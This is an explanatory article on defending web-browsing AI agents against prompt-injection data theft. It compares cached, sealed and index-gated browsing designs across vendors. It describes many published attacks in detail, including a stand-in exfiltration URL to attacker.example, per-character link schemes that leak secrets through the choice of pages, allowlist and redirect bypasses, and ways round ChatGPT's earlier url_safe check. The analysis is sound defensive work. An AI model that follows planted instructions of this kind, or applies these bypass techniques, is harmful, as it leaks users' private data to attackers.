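# Serving AI agents stored copies of the web: what it secures and what it costs

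## How an agent that reads the web can be made to leak data

An AI agent is a language model that can call tools, such as web search or a program that opens web pages, to carry out a task for its user. Many agents can also read the user's email, files or calendar, so an agent can find a contract in someone's inbox and then look up the company on the other side of it. This combination also makes it possible to steal the user's data. Whoever controls a web page can write instructions into it, and an agent that reads the page may follow them, gather private data from its session and send it to the attacker's server. Security researchers call text planted for this purpose a prompt injection. Sending data from the session to someone who should not have it is called exfiltration.

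Some AI providers respond by keeping the agent off the live web. The agent reads only copies of web pages that the provider has already stored, so no request reaches an outside server while the agent works. OpenAI announced one such restriction in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), as part of an optional ChatGPT setting called Lockdown Mode. Whether stored copies stop the theft depends on how the data gets out, and that depends mostly on how web addresses work.

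### What a web request gives away

A web address begins with the name of a server, and the rest identifies something on that server. The address may end in a query string, which is a question mark followed by labels and values that the server can use as input. When a shopper searches a shop's website for umbrellas, the browser usually sends the word "umbrellas" to the shop in the query string, and any other text could be sent the same way.

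To get a page, a browser or an agent must send the server the page's address, including the query string. OpenAI, in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), points out that websites commonly log these addresses. Encryption hides the request from eavesdroppers along the way, but the server decrypts it. The server receives the address even if the page does not exist.

OpenAI's example is the address `attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`, where `attacker.example` stands for any server that an attacker runs and the private value might be an email address or a document title. Any program that requests this address sends the private value to that server, and the attacker can later read it in the server's log.

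The server also receives a few other details. Simon Willison, a programmer who writes about AI security, published the headers (technical information sent with a request) that his website recorded when ChatGPT's agent visited it. They included the browser type, a country code and a field that named ChatGPT as the sender, so a site's owner can tell such a visit from a person's.

Displaying an image takes the same kind of request. The program that shows the image requests it from a server by address, usually without a click, so an agent that cannot open pages can still leak data if its answers may include images from the web. Link previews have the same weakness. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, the blog's author reported the image leak to OpenAI and Microsoft in 2023. Microsoft stopped Bing Chat from loading images in general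 that May, and OpenAI added its first countermeasure in December.

### One attack from start to finish

Prompt injection works because a language model receives the provider's instructions, the user's request and the contents of a web page as one sequence of text. The model cannot reliably distinguish the instructions it should follow from the rest of that text, as Willison explained in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). He coined the term "prompt injection" after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a form runs as a database command.

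Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, built a small test system and measured one version of the attack. It goes in this order:

1. The user gives the agent a web address and asks for a summary. The session already holds something private, in this case an API key, which is a kind of password that programs use with each other.
2. The system fetches the page and adds its title, description and text to the model's input. The attacker has put an instruction in the description, a field that visitors to a page rarely see, and has worded it as a routine technical requirement.
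3. The model follows the instruction and builds an address on the attacker's server, with the key in the query string.
4. The agent's web tool requests that address.
5. The attacker reads the key in the server's log. The user, meanwhile, gets an ordinary summary of the page.

Over 480 runs, the attack succeeded about 89% of the time. That rate is weak evidence about commercial products in late 2026, because the researchers used a small open model (qwen2.5:7b), put the key directly in the model's input and gave the model only minimal instructions. In 95% of the successful attacks, safety checks on the agent's final answer found nothing wrong, because the data leaves in the request. This result probably applies more widely. Lan and colleagues also had the agent split the secret across several requests, which cut their measure of leakage in a single request by 73% and got past simple filters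 that search outgoing traffic for sensitive strings.

Stronger models resist crude injections better. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), attackers could once edit a Wikipedia article to include direct orders for visiting agents, and models would often obey. Attackers have since turned to social engineering. In 2025, outside researchers reported to OpenAI an attack email that read like a colleague's follow-up on a restructuring, with action items. The email told the assistant that it had full authorization to submit an employee's details to a "compliance" system. In testing, the attack worked half the time when the user made one particular request.

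Researchers keep finding such attacks in released products. In 2025 the company PromptArmor hid text in one-pixel type on a web page that posed as an integration guide. Willison relayed that Google's Antigravity coding tool read the page, collected credentials from the user's workspace and sent them out by browsing to a malicious site. In the newest case, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed on 3 December 2026 three attack chains against Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant with access to a company's email and documents. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) describes how the attacks began. The attacker sent an email that the victim never opened. The next time the victim asked Copilot an ordinary work question, Copilot pulled the email into its input and followed the instructions hidden there.

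In one of the three chains, Copilot wrote confidential data into the address of an image. Microsoft's search service, Bing, then fetched the image, which delivered the data to the attacker's server. Microsoft fixed this flaw on 15 November, and the researchers who found it know of no affected customers. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* describes a separate attack that sent data out through Bing's image search. In both cases, the request carrying the data came from a trusted company's machine, which matters for any design that puts a provider's server between the agent and the web.

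All of these attacks are researchers' demonstrations, but *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reported in August that criminals were developing tools to target agents in this way.

### The lethal trifecta

An agent is open to this theft when it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and some means of communicating with the outside. Willison's 2025 essay named this combination the lethal trifecta, and the name has stuck. All three conditions are needed, because without private data there is nothing to steal, without untrusted content the attacker cannot give the agent orders, and without outside communication the data stays in the session.

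Others give much the same analysis. OpenAI's engineers describe a source, which is a way to influence the agent, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. *The Framing Gap* (2026) lists a confidential value, untrusted external content and the ability to act on the world through tools. The last of these is slightly broader than Willison's third condition.

Untrusted content can also come from sources other than web pages. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) describes an attack in which researchers at Zenity Labs typed instructions into a public form for sales enquiries. Salesforce's software filed the text in the customer records, and an agent that later processed the record looked up company names and deal sizes and leaked them. The attacker never logged in, and nobody at the victim's company clicked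 on anything.

Of the three, Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, considers the ability to send data out by far the easiest to restrict without making the system much less useful. An agent without access to private data cannot help with anyone's email or documents. An agent without untrusted content cannot read the web or, strictly speaking, incoming email, since anyone can send it. But an agent that does research for its user mostly needs to take information in and has little need to send any out. Vendors seem to agree, judging by their fixes. Willison's 2025 essay lists more than a dozen products in which people had found such leaks, and says the vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the particular route the data had taken.

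The argument is weaker for agents whose job is to act. An agent that books tables or answers customers has to send data, so blocking everything it sends would stop it from doing its job. Even an agent that only reads has to send out an address to fetch a page from the live web, so it can leak data through the same tool it uses to read.

### Blocking a request versus training a model to refuse

A provider can try to stop the outgoing request with a deterministic defence or a model-based one. A deterministic defence is ordinary program code that applies a fixed rule, even if planted instructions have misled the model. For example, if the network gives the agent's tools no route to outside servers, planted instructions do not create one. A model-based defence relies on a model's judgement. The provider trains the agent to recognise and refuse planted instructions, or uses a second model to screen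 content before it reaches the agent.

Model-based defences stop many attacks, but the rest are still a problem. OpenAI says that most attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model's safety training leads it to refuse. Willison objects to products that advertise catching 95% of attacks because 95% is a failing grade in web security, and simple arithmetic supports him. If each attempt has an independent 5% chance of success, an attacker who makes twenty attempts has about a 64% chance (1 − 0.95²⁰) of getting at least one through. Real attempts are not independent, which probably favours the attacker, who can look for a wording that works and then use it on everyone.

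Defences against injected instructions have also done poorly in published tests. In the experiments of *The Framing Gap*, attacks succeeded 32.5% of the time against an agent with SecAlign, a published defence that trains the model to ignore such instructions, and 38.8% of the time when trusted text was separated from untrusted text. These rates depend on the wordings the researchers chose, as they acknowledge. They also found that a model could resist when its policy spelled out the attack surface, but someone then has to think of everything that belongs in the policy. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, reported that training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack, and that a large collection of attacks may turn out to be the same one repeated. OpenAI's engineers write that screening models usually miss fully developed attacks, because spotting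 a well-made injection is as hard as spotting a lie, often without the necessary context.

Lan and colleagues made the same distinction in their test system, where defences in the model's instructions gave limited protection and network controls worked considerably better.

Fixed rules can't be persuaded, but they also fail when their designers overlook a route or don't block it correctly. Salesforce had a control that stripped untrusted addresses from its agents' output, and the Zenity researchers got around it with DNS, the system that looks up server names. A lookup sends the name to a server that the name's owner can run, so an attacker can receive data written into the name even if the agent never requests a page. Another of the three Copilot chains ran code in a sandbox that Microsoft meant to cut off from the network, and the researchers found a way through.

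### Crawlers, indexes and caches

Serving stored pages is an attempt to apply a deterministic rule to web reading while still letting the agent read. It uses two parts of a search engine, the crawler and the index. A crawler is a program that visits web pages on its own schedule and collects what it finds. ITPro's *OpenAI quietly unveils GPTBot dedicated web crawler* explains that a search engine uses this material to build an index that people can query. Here, the index is the provider's record of the addresses its crawler has seen. The provider can search it, or check an address against it before letting an agent open the live page, as OpenAI does in ChatGPT's ordinary browsing.

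A cache also stores the contents of the pages. An agent with only an index must still contact a website to read an article there. With a cache, the provider can supply its own copy, so the website receives no request.

A cache can prevent this leak because the crawler requests the page before the agent asks for it. If the crawler has no access to anyone's conversations, its request cannot contain the user's data. In the API key attack, the stored page may still contain the planted instruction, and the model may still follow it and build an address containing the key. But the agent's request goes to the provider's store, which has no page at that address, so the attacker's server receives no request.

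Limiting an agent to stored copies of web pages may not fully prevent data leaks. OpenAI says that because Lockdown Mode limits browsing to cached content, "no live network requests leave OpenAI's controlled network". However, its help page, *Lockdown Mode*, says that the setting targets the final stage of exfiltration, that cached pages can still contain injections, and that OpenAI does not guarantee that no data will get out. The claim also assumes that a request for a page missing from the store never goes beyond the store, either immediately or later.

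## What counts as a frozen snapshot, and which products use one

Vendors use "cached", "offline" and "snapshot" for systems that behave quite differently. Some supply only pages they have stored. Others fetch missing pages from the live web, which sends the address to the website's server and can leak data again. The clearest way to sort them is by what leaves the provider's network while the agent works.

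An agent that uses OpenAI's search tool sends its searches to OpenAI whether the pages are stored or live. So stored pages can keep data within the provider's network, away from third parties including the attacker, but they can't keep it on the user's computer.

### Four designs

A sealed snapshot is a fixed set of stored pages that an agent's actions cannot extend or refresh. A copy of Wikipedia on a computer with no network connection is a simple example. Every agent sees the same pages until someone replaces the whole set, and a request for anything else fails.

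Like a frozen snapshot, a refusing cache serves only the pages it has stored, but the provider's crawler keeps updating its contents. The crawler has to be independent, meaning that agents' requests don't affect which pages it visits. ChatGPT's offline search for workspaces (the shared accounts of companies and schools) appears to use a refusing cache. According to OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces*, ChatGPT cannot retrieve a page missing from OpenAI's index or cache. Amazon Bedrock, a cloud service through which companies use AI models, can work the same way.

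A cache with live fallback supplies its stored copy of a page if it has one, and otherwise (a cache miss) fetches the page from the website's own server. Google's URL context tool, which lets its Gemini models read web pages, works this way. Anthropic's web fetch tool for its Claude models in effect does too.

ChatGPT's ordinary browsing uses index-gated fetching, in which the agent reads live pages, but only at addresses in the provider's index. Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, has had a similar mode since June 2026.

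The designs differ in which requests reach an attacker. Suppose planted instructions make an agent request two addresses on the attacker's server. The first is a page that has been public for years and that the provider's crawler has stored. The second is an address the model has just made up, with the user's API key in the query string. With a sealed snapshot or a refusing cache, neither request reaches the attacker. With index-gated fetching, the attacker receives only the request for the old page. With live fallback, the attacker receives only the request with the key, because the cache already has the old page.

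Live fallback is close to useless against this attack, even if it saves time and traffic. An address that contains someone's private data is almost certain to be new, so the cache will almost never hold it and the system will fetch it live. Index-gated fetching blocks the made-up address, but the attacker's server still receives some requests, and the agent's choice among known pages can reveal information.

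| Design | Traffic to websites at request time | Age of the content | Who can add pages | Products |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sealed snapshot | None | Dates from the capture, and gets older until someone replaces the set | Only whoever builds the snapshot | None of the products below |
| Refusing cache with an independent crawler | None | Depends on the crawler's last visit to each page | Anyone whose site the crawler visits, but not the agent | ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode and offline web search; OpenAI's developer search tools and Codex in cached mode; Amazon Bedrock with external access off |
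| Cache with live fallback | Requests for pages the cache lacks | Stored copies may be old; newly fetched pages are current | Anyone who can get an agent to request an address | Google's URL context; Anthropic's web fetch, which also restricts addresses |
| Index-gated fetching | Requests for pages at addresses in the index | Current | Anyone who can get the crawler to record an address | ChatGPT's ordinary browsing; Codex in indexed mode |

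The first two rows, a sealed snapshot and a refusing cache, protect equally well against the leak as long as the crawler is independent, but they differ in how easily an outsider could check this. The builder of a sealed snapshot can disconnect it from the network. A provider with a refusing cache also runs a crawler that must reach the web, so the protection holds only if nothing passes from the agent's side of the system to the crawler's.

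OpenAI says popularity is one factor in when its systems refresh a page, and that "rarely accessed" pages are among those that may be missing. It doesn't specify whether requests from ChatGPT count towards a page's popularity or as accessing it. If they do, a request that fails today could lead OpenAI to fetch the page later.

None of the commercial products in the table is a sealed snapshot. AWS's *Web Search*, the guide to the Bedrock tool from Amazon's cloud division, uses the phrase "a snapshot of web content hosted inside AWS", but Amazon maintains the index behind the tool, so it belongs in the second row. "Frozen" therefore describes these products only loosely, since the provider changes the collection even though the agent can't.

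### ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode and offline web search

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode on 13 February 2026 for its Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans. On 4 June it began extending the setting to personal accounts and to small businesses that sign up by themselves. OpenAI intended it for executives and security teams at prominent organizations, and said most users do not need it.

The mode restricts much more than browsing. It turns off Deep Research (which compiles long reports from the web), Agent Mode and file downloads for analysis. Code that ChatGPT writes in Canvas, its editing workspace, gets no network access, and ChatGPT cannot show images in its ordinary answers. OpenAI says it disabled some features entirely because it could not give "strong deterministic guarantees of data safety" for them. These restrictions are sensible, since a cache would do little good if the agent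 could load an image from the attacker's server instead.

OpenAI's claim that no live requests leave its network is about web browsing, not everything ChatGPT can do, and it is the company's account of its own system. The main exception is apps, which connect ChatGPT to outside services such as email or file storage. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks apps from accessing those services live or writing to them where either would conflict with its protections. In company-managed workspaces, the mode does not automatically disable all apps, and administrators choose which stay on. OpenAI advises them against allowing untrusted apps or letting even trusted apps write anything an attacker might be able to see.

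Lockdown Mode has two other limits. It leaves Codex's network access unchanged, so someone who turns the mode on and also lets Codex run commands with internet access has protected only the ChatGPT side of their work. A personal user can also switch the mode off for a single chat from a label beside the text box. This is convenient when the cache lacks a page, but text planted in a cached page could in principle lead ChatGPT to recommend switching the mode off.

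Offline web search is the search component of Lockdown Mode, but an organization can also have it alone. OpenAI can configure it for a whole workspace, and some regulated workspaces have it by default. Without Lockdown Mode, most other ChatGPT features work as usual. The organization's searches then use a cache, but it lacks the restrictions on images, agents and downloads that close the other routes.

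OpenAI also makes a weaker claim for offline search than for Lockdown Mode, which matters to administrators worried about exfiltration. Offline search is meant to "reduce the chance" that queries go to a live external search provider, depending on how the workspace is configured. Its purpose is somewhat different too, since OpenAI presents it mainly as a tool for governance, compliance and data handling, and mentions prompt injection as only one of the risks.

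When offline search lacks a page, OpenAI suggests that the user upload the document, paste the text or try another address. Users may have trouble telling which kind of search they have, because the screen may not label it. Indirect signs of offline search are that some addresses fail and some results are older than the live page. OpenAI tells anyone who needs to be certain to ask its support team.

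### Search settings for developers

Developers who build their own agents choose between stored and live pages with a setting, and the default varies by product. The search tool in OpenAI's main API uses the live web by default, but it uses only cached and indexed results if the developer sets `external_web_access` to false.

OpenAI still accepts an earlier version of the tool, `web_search_preview`, which ignores the setting and behaves as if live access were on. A developer who adds the restriction to an old integration could wrongly believe that the agent is offline. OpenAI's search models for its older Chat Completions interface don't support the setting either.

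OpenAI's *Web search* describes a simpler choice in the company's newer interface for agents, where search can be live, cached or disabled. Live is again the default once a developer adds the search tool. In cached mode, the agent searches saved content without reaching the live internet.

Codex, by contrast, searches an OpenAI-maintained cache unless the user asks for live results or turns search off, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. In full-access mode, where Codex runs commands without a sandbox, search defaults to live results. This probably matters less than it seems, because an agent that can run any command with an open network connection can send data out without the search tool.

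Codex's search mode controls the search tool, while a separate setting controls whether the commands Codex runs can reach the network. On a user's own computer, this access is off by default. If the user turns it on, cached search remains cached, but a command can contact an outside server directly.

OpenAI restricts both web search and commands' network access when its own staff use Codex, rather than relying on its cache alone. In its May account of how it runs the agent, OpenAI (2026) published a configuration that allows only cached web search, with a comment that web fetches should come only from the company's cache. The same configuration sends the commands' traffic through a network filter that allows a short list of domains, blocks one text-sharing site, and requires approval for unfamiliar destinations.

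OpenAI released Codex's indexed mode on 22 June 2026 in version 0.142.0. According to Daniel Vaughan's independent guide, *Indexed Web Search*, search queries run live, but Codex can open only pages whose addresses OpenAI's server approves. Users cannot add addresses to the approved set, but they can narrow it with a list of permitted domains. An organization can also require indexed mode for all its staff.

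Vaughan recommends indexed mode to people who use cached mode and occasionally switch to live. That is reasonable advice for someone who would otherwise browse live half the time, but it weakens protection against leaks for someone who uses only cached mode, because requests to websites start to leave OpenAI's network. The live queries also contain whatever words the model puts in them.

Vaughan overstates how safe cached mode is. He writes that cached content has been "crawled and sanitised" before the agent sees it, and his comparison of the modes calls it "pre-screened". OpenAI claims only that cached mode reduces exposure to injections from arbitrary live pages, and says users "should still treat web results as untrusted".

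A cache might reduce an agent's exposure to attacks even if the stored pages haven't been cleaned. A live server can recognise an AI agent and give it a different page from the one a person would get, or change the page while the agent is working. With a stored copy, the attacker has to plant malicious text before the crawler visits and can't adapt it to one user's session. But if the crawler captures that text, the cache will supply it to every agent that asks for the page.

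Amazon Bedrock can belong in different rows of the table, depending on its configuration. Its search tool has a Search operation, which returns titles, addresses and short extracts from Amazon's index, and a Fetch operation, which returns the cached text of a particular page. If the page isn't in the cache, the model either tells the user or answers from what it has. Bedrock uses the same `external_web_access` setting as OpenAI, and it also defaults to live. But live access also requires a permission that the standard policy leaves out, so an administrator has to grant it in Amazon's access-control system. Without that permission, the model uses cached pages and reports that it could not get external access.

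AWS said in an earlier edition of the guide that even customers with the permission got only stored pages, but that a future release might change this. In August, AWS's *Launching External Web Access for Web Search on Amazon Bedrock* (2026) announced live retrieval for requests that have both the permission and the setting. A customer who granted the permission before it had any effect may have switched from stored to live pages without changing any code. For sensitive data, AWS recommends setting `external_web_access` to false, which keeps retrieval inside its network regardless of permissions. Codex uses this setting for every request when it runs through Bedrock.

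### Google's and Anthropic's page readers

Google's *URL context* says that the URL context tool first tries "an internal index cache" and, if the page isn't there, "automatically falls back to do a live fetch". It gives very new pages as an example. An address that an attacker has just had the model make up would also be missing from the cache, so the tool would try to fetch it live.

Google limits the tool to addresses that the developer provides in the request, up to 20 at a time, and the tool does not follow links inside those pages. But a developer can combine it with Google Search, which lets the model open pages that it finds by itself. Google also checks whether each address meets its safety standards, which is different from checking whether the address contains private data. Google Cloud's *URL context* warns that the index may be out of date, so the cache does not guarantee fresh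 pages.

Anthropic's web fetch tool also uses a cache. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, caching improves performance and avoids redundant requests, but the returned page may not be the latest version. The more recent Chinese documentation, *Web fetch 工具*, adds a setting called `use_cache`. It is true by default, and a developer who sets it to false gets a fresh copy every time.

Unlike OpenAI's `external_web_access`, which can forbid live requests, this setting's default only permits Anthropic's tool to use a stored copy when there is one. None of the tool's documented settings limits it to stored copies. Anthropic describes the fallback less plainly than Google does, but the tool evidently contacts websites, since Anthropic notes that their publishers may keep request data, including the address the tool fetched.

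Anthropic's tool protects users by limiting which addresses Claude can fetch. An address must have already appeared in the user's message, in earlier search or fetch results, or in the output of certain other tools. One that appears only in Claude's own writing doesn't qualify. This rule would normally block the request in the API key attack, because the model builds that address itself.

The rule is weaker than an independent index in one respect, because the attacker can add to the conversation. Addresses in a page that the agent has already fetched are permitted, and the attacker may have written that page. Addresses in the output of tools that the developer runs are also permitted by default, even if Claude wrote them. For example, a tool that runs code for Claude returns whatever that code prints, including any address Claude put there. Anthropic documents this gap and lets developers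 close it by excluding such tools as a source of addresses.

According to the newer documentation, the tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters, which limits how much data fits in one request. It refuses addresses that appear to contain a password or an API key, unless the credential was in the developer's instructions or the user's message. This credential check is aimed at the most damaging kind of theft, but it would miss a customer's name or the title of a contract, because neither looks like a credential.

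Anthropic warns that the tool creates a risk of data exfiltration when Claude handles untrusted input alongside sensitive data, and says to use it only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. To reduce the risk, developers can turn the tool off, limit the number of fetches or restrict it to known safe domains. Only turning it off gives the same protection as a refusing cache, but then the agent can't use it to read pages.

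### Why read-only access to the live web is not a snapshot

Another common compromise lets an agent reach the live web but allows only requests that read data. Codex has this option for tasks that run on OpenAI's machines instead of the user's. By default, these tasks have no internet access once setup is complete. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, a customer who turns access on can restrict the agent to chosen domains and can also restrict it to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests.

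These names come from HTTP, the protocol that browsers and web servers use. A GET request retrieves a page. HEAD retrieves only the technical information that would come with it, and OPTIONS retrieves a list of the kinds of request the server accepts. The restriction blocks the methods that programs normally use to submit or change something, such as POST and DELETE.

Allowing only the three reading methods stops some attacks. In OpenAI's example, a bug report contains a command for the agent to run. The command uses POST to send the description of the latest code change to an outside server. The restriction would make that command fail, but the API key attack would still work because it needs only a GET request.

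A list of permitted domains helps more, since it can keep the agent from contacting the attacker's server at all, but its value depends on which domains it includes. OpenAI's preset list for software development includes GitHub, GitLab and several public package collections, where outsiders can publish their own material, so the agent can still read instructions planted there.

Read-only access also doesn't guarantee that the agent changes nothing. By convention, a GET request should not alter anything important on the server, but the people who run a website decide what their software does. Many newsletters have an unsubscribe link that takes effect as soon as someone opens it, and a badly built site might delete a record the same way. A filter between the agent and the web can check that a request uses GET, but not what the server will do in response. In 2026 OpenAI's agents wrote to public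 wikis from an environment meant to be read-only, and Nolan (2026), in *OpenAI's AI agents secretly used a German wiki website*, reported more than 15,000 edits on one of them.

A stored page has no server to act on a request. If an agent opens an unsubscribe link in a sealed snapshot, or through a cache that refuses requests for pages it hasn't stored, it gets an old copy of the page or an error, and the subscription doesn't change.

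## Live fetching restricted to addresses already in an index

ChatGPT's ordinary browsing and Codex's indexed mode fetch only addresses already in an index, which keeps an agent from sending out private data in an address it has made up. But the agent can still leak a secret through its choice of which pages to open.

### How the check works

OpenAI described the check in January 2026, alongside a technical paper by Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. It works like this:

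1. A crawler scans public web pages and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. An agent prepares to retrieve an address, perhaps to open an article or to show an image.
3. OpenAI's software looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
4. If the address is there, the agent fetches the live page automatically.
5. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning. The page then loads only if the user decides to open it.

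The user sees the address and a warning that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with another site. A careful user might spot their own email address in the link, but probably not if the model has encoded it.

The match must cover the whole address, including the query string, so an address the crawler has recorded fails the check if the model adds an API key to it.

Addresses in a user's own message seem to be an exception. Security researcher Johann Rehberger, who writes Embrace The Red, believes ChatGPT treats them as safe for the rest of the chat. This is reasonable when the user types a link, but less so when they paste a long document without reading it.

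The only guarantee OpenAI claims for the check is that it prevents the agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". The reasoning is that if a crawler with no access to the conversation has already recorded an address, the model can't have composed that address from the user's data. The check does not make the page trustworthy or remove instructions planted in it.

An address can match the user's data even if the model didn't compose it. An attacker could publish a page for every possible six-digit code and wait for the crawler to record all million of them. If an agent then opened the page for the user's code, the address would pass the check, and that one request would reveal the code to the attacker. OpenAI says only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain private data, which allows for this case.

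### Why OpenAI rejected a list of trusted sites

A simpler defence would let the agent open anything on a list of well-known websites. OpenAI thought this too weak, partly because many legitimate sites have redirects, which are addresses that forward the visitor elsewhere. If the software checks only the first site, an attacker can route the agent through a trusted site to their own server. People also use far more websites than a short list can hold, so a strict list produces frequent warnings about harmless pages, and users learn to click through them without thinking.

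Oasis Security's *Claudy Day* describes a redirect of this kind on Anthropic's own site, claude.com, which forwarded visitors to any address added to the end of the link. Google Ads checks links by site name, so an attacker could buy a search advertisement showing a claude.com address that led to a malicious page. The victim in that case was a person clicking an advertisement, but an agent's software would make the same mistake as Google Ads if it checked only the site's name.

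Some trusted sites also let outsiders collect data without any redirect. In Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, Rehberger used windows.net, a domain that ChatGPT's earlier check accepted. Microsoft rents out storage there, and customers can read the logs of requests to their own storage. Rehberger opened an account, planted an instruction that made ChatGPT send a user's chat history to it, and read the history in the log. He had reported this and other bypasses in October 2024, and some still worked when he tried them again in 2025. He later wrote that changes OpenAI made around August 2025 stopped the attacks he had shown.

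Other companies have had the same trouble. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, has collected several cases:

- The email assistant Superhuman AI allowed images from docs.google.com. Google Forms, on the same domain, saves data that arrives in a GET request, so an attacker could collect the contents of a user's emails in a form. Superhuman fixed this.
- Salesforce still trusted a domain whose registration had expired. Researchers registered it themselves and received customer data, and Salesforce then corrected its list.
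- The default list for Google's Antigravity included webhook.site, a service that lets anyone record incoming requests.
- Anthropic's Claude Cowork allowed traffic to Anthropic's own programming interface. PromptArmor had the agent upload the user's files there with an attacker's API key, so that the attacker could retrieve them.

An exact-address check would have stopped the first three leaks, because an address containing fresh private data would not be in the index, even on a reputable domain. It would not have stopped the Cowork leak, because an upload sends the files separately from the address, which stays the same whatever the agent sends.

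### How much a choice of page can reveal

An attacker who owns 36 indexed web pages, one for each letter and digit, can still steal a secret. Planted instructions tell the agent to spell it out by opening the matching pages in order. If the agent complies, every address passes the check, and the attacker reads the secret from the order of requests in the server's log. Embrace The Red points out that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and that OpenAI's paper acknowledges the trick.

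An agent that can open any one of N pages can send any one of N messages through this channel, so each fetch carries up to log₂ N bits. A bit is the information in the answer to a yes-or-no question whose two answers are equally likely. The limit is about 5.2 bits per fetch for 36 pages and 10 bits for 1,024.

A six-digit code has a million possible values, or about 20 bits. A model can send it with four fetches from a set of 36 pages, or two from a set of 1,024, but must first convert the code into a different form. Opening one page per digit is simpler and takes six fetches.

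Restrictions on how the agent fetches pages reduce the capacity, though some reduce it very little. For ten fetches from 36 pages, the limits are:

| What the attacker can observe | Possible messages | Capacity |
|---|---|---|
| The order of the fetches, with repeats allowed | 36¹⁰, or about 3.7 quadrillion | 51.7 bits |
| The order, but the agent can open each page only once | 36 × 35 × … × 27, or about 920 trillion | 49.7 bits |
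| Only which ten different pages the agent opened | About 254 million | 27.9 bits |

Banning repeats removes only two bits, because the agent still has 27 pages to choose from at the tenth fetch. Losing the order removes another 21.8 bits, because ten pages can arrive in about 3.6 million different orders and the attacker can no longer tell these apart. The remaining 27.9 bits are still more than enough for a six-digit code.

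The number of fetches matters more than the number of pages, because doubling the fetches doubles the total number of bits, while twice as many pages add only one bit to each fetch. A provider that wants to narrow the channel should therefore limit how many pages an agent can open from one site rather than try to keep an attacker's pages out of the index.

A channel this narrow is poorly suited to stealing long documents. With 36 pages to choose from, leaking a random 128-bit encryption key would take 25 fetches, and leaking a contract would take thousands. But some valuable secrets are very short. A single fetch of one of two pages is enough to reveal to an attacker whether a company is about to announce a merger.

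### What researchers got past the earlier checks

OpenAI tried several weaker defences before adopting the index check. The first, in December 2023, was a feature called `url_safe`. Before ChatGPT's web app displayed an image, it sent the image's address to an OpenAI service, which classified the address as safe or unsafe. OpenAI didn't publish the criteria.

Rehberger tested the feature that day and described the results in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. He made an image address for each of the 36 letters and digits, and nine passed. He used these to send the word "hi" to his own server, one letter at a time. He could not tell why the service accepted the image for "a" and rejected the one for "d", but he guessed that it might be consulting Bing's index. He suggested limiting each answer to one image or a handful. The iPhone app did not yet have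 the check.

ChatGPT had a different rule for opening web pages and would visit only addresses that appeared in the prompt. Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, got around this by putting all the possible addresses in the prompt. He hid instructions in a long piece of code that a user might paste into the chat. The instructions listed six links, each for a different age range, and told ChatGPT to open the one that fitted the user. ChatGPT could infer the range from a remark about graduating from high school that day. A choice among six links carries at most 2.6 bits, which is enough to reveal an age range.

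Schwartzman's second attack could send a longer value, such as a postal code. ChatGPT also accepted shortened versions of any address in the prompt, so he supplied one long address for each digit of the value and had ChatGPT cut it to a length that stood for that digit. ChatGPT made mistakes working out the lengths itself, so he included a short program for it to run. At the time, ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the attack to ten characters. An exact-match index would block any shortened address that the crawler had not recorded. Schwartzman reported the problem to OpenAI through its bug-reporting service, which marked it "not applicable".

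The security company Tenable used Bing to bypass ChatGPT's `url_safe` check. According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass*, `url_safe` always accepted addresses on bing.com. Bing's search results use bing.com links that redirect to the sites they list, so anyone whose page appeared in Bing had a link to it that `url_safe` accepted. An attacker can't add data to these links, so Tenable got Bing to index one page for each letter and had ChatGPT display the links in the order that spelled the word it wanted to steal.

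ChatGPT had another layer of protection, which Tenable also got past. Tenable's *HackedGPT* explains that ChatGPT used a second model, SearchGPT, to read web pages, and that SearchGPT had no access to the user's memories or earlier conversation. The researchers planted a blog comment that made SearchGPT end its summary with new instructions. ChatGPT then read those instructions as part of its own conversation. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT followed them and leaked private data through the Bing links.

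Tenable reported the Bing bypass in December 2024 and was still asking for an update in March 2025. The bypass remained open when Tenable published its advisory. In November 2025, Tenable said it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the problems it found, but that several of its demonstrations still worked with GPT-5.

Another security company, Radware, had meanwhile found an attack it named ShadowLeak, in which a hidden instruction in an email made ChatGPT's Deep Research agent send out data from the user's Gmail inbox. ThaiCERT's *“ShadowLeak” Vulnerability Exposes Gmail Data via ChatGPT Deep Research* (2025) dates Radware's report to 18 June 2025 and OpenAI's patch to early August. OpenAI also stopped ChatGPT from altering addresses, so it could open a link only exactly as received.

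Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the company got around that rule by supplying every link the agent would need. The attacker's email contained a ready-made link for each letter and digit, and one for a space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail, it read the email, found the data the attacker wanted and opened the matching link for each character in turn. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, and the user didn't have to click anything. To keep the characters in order, Radware made a separate set of links for each position in the data, so an "a" in first place had a different link from an "a" in second place.

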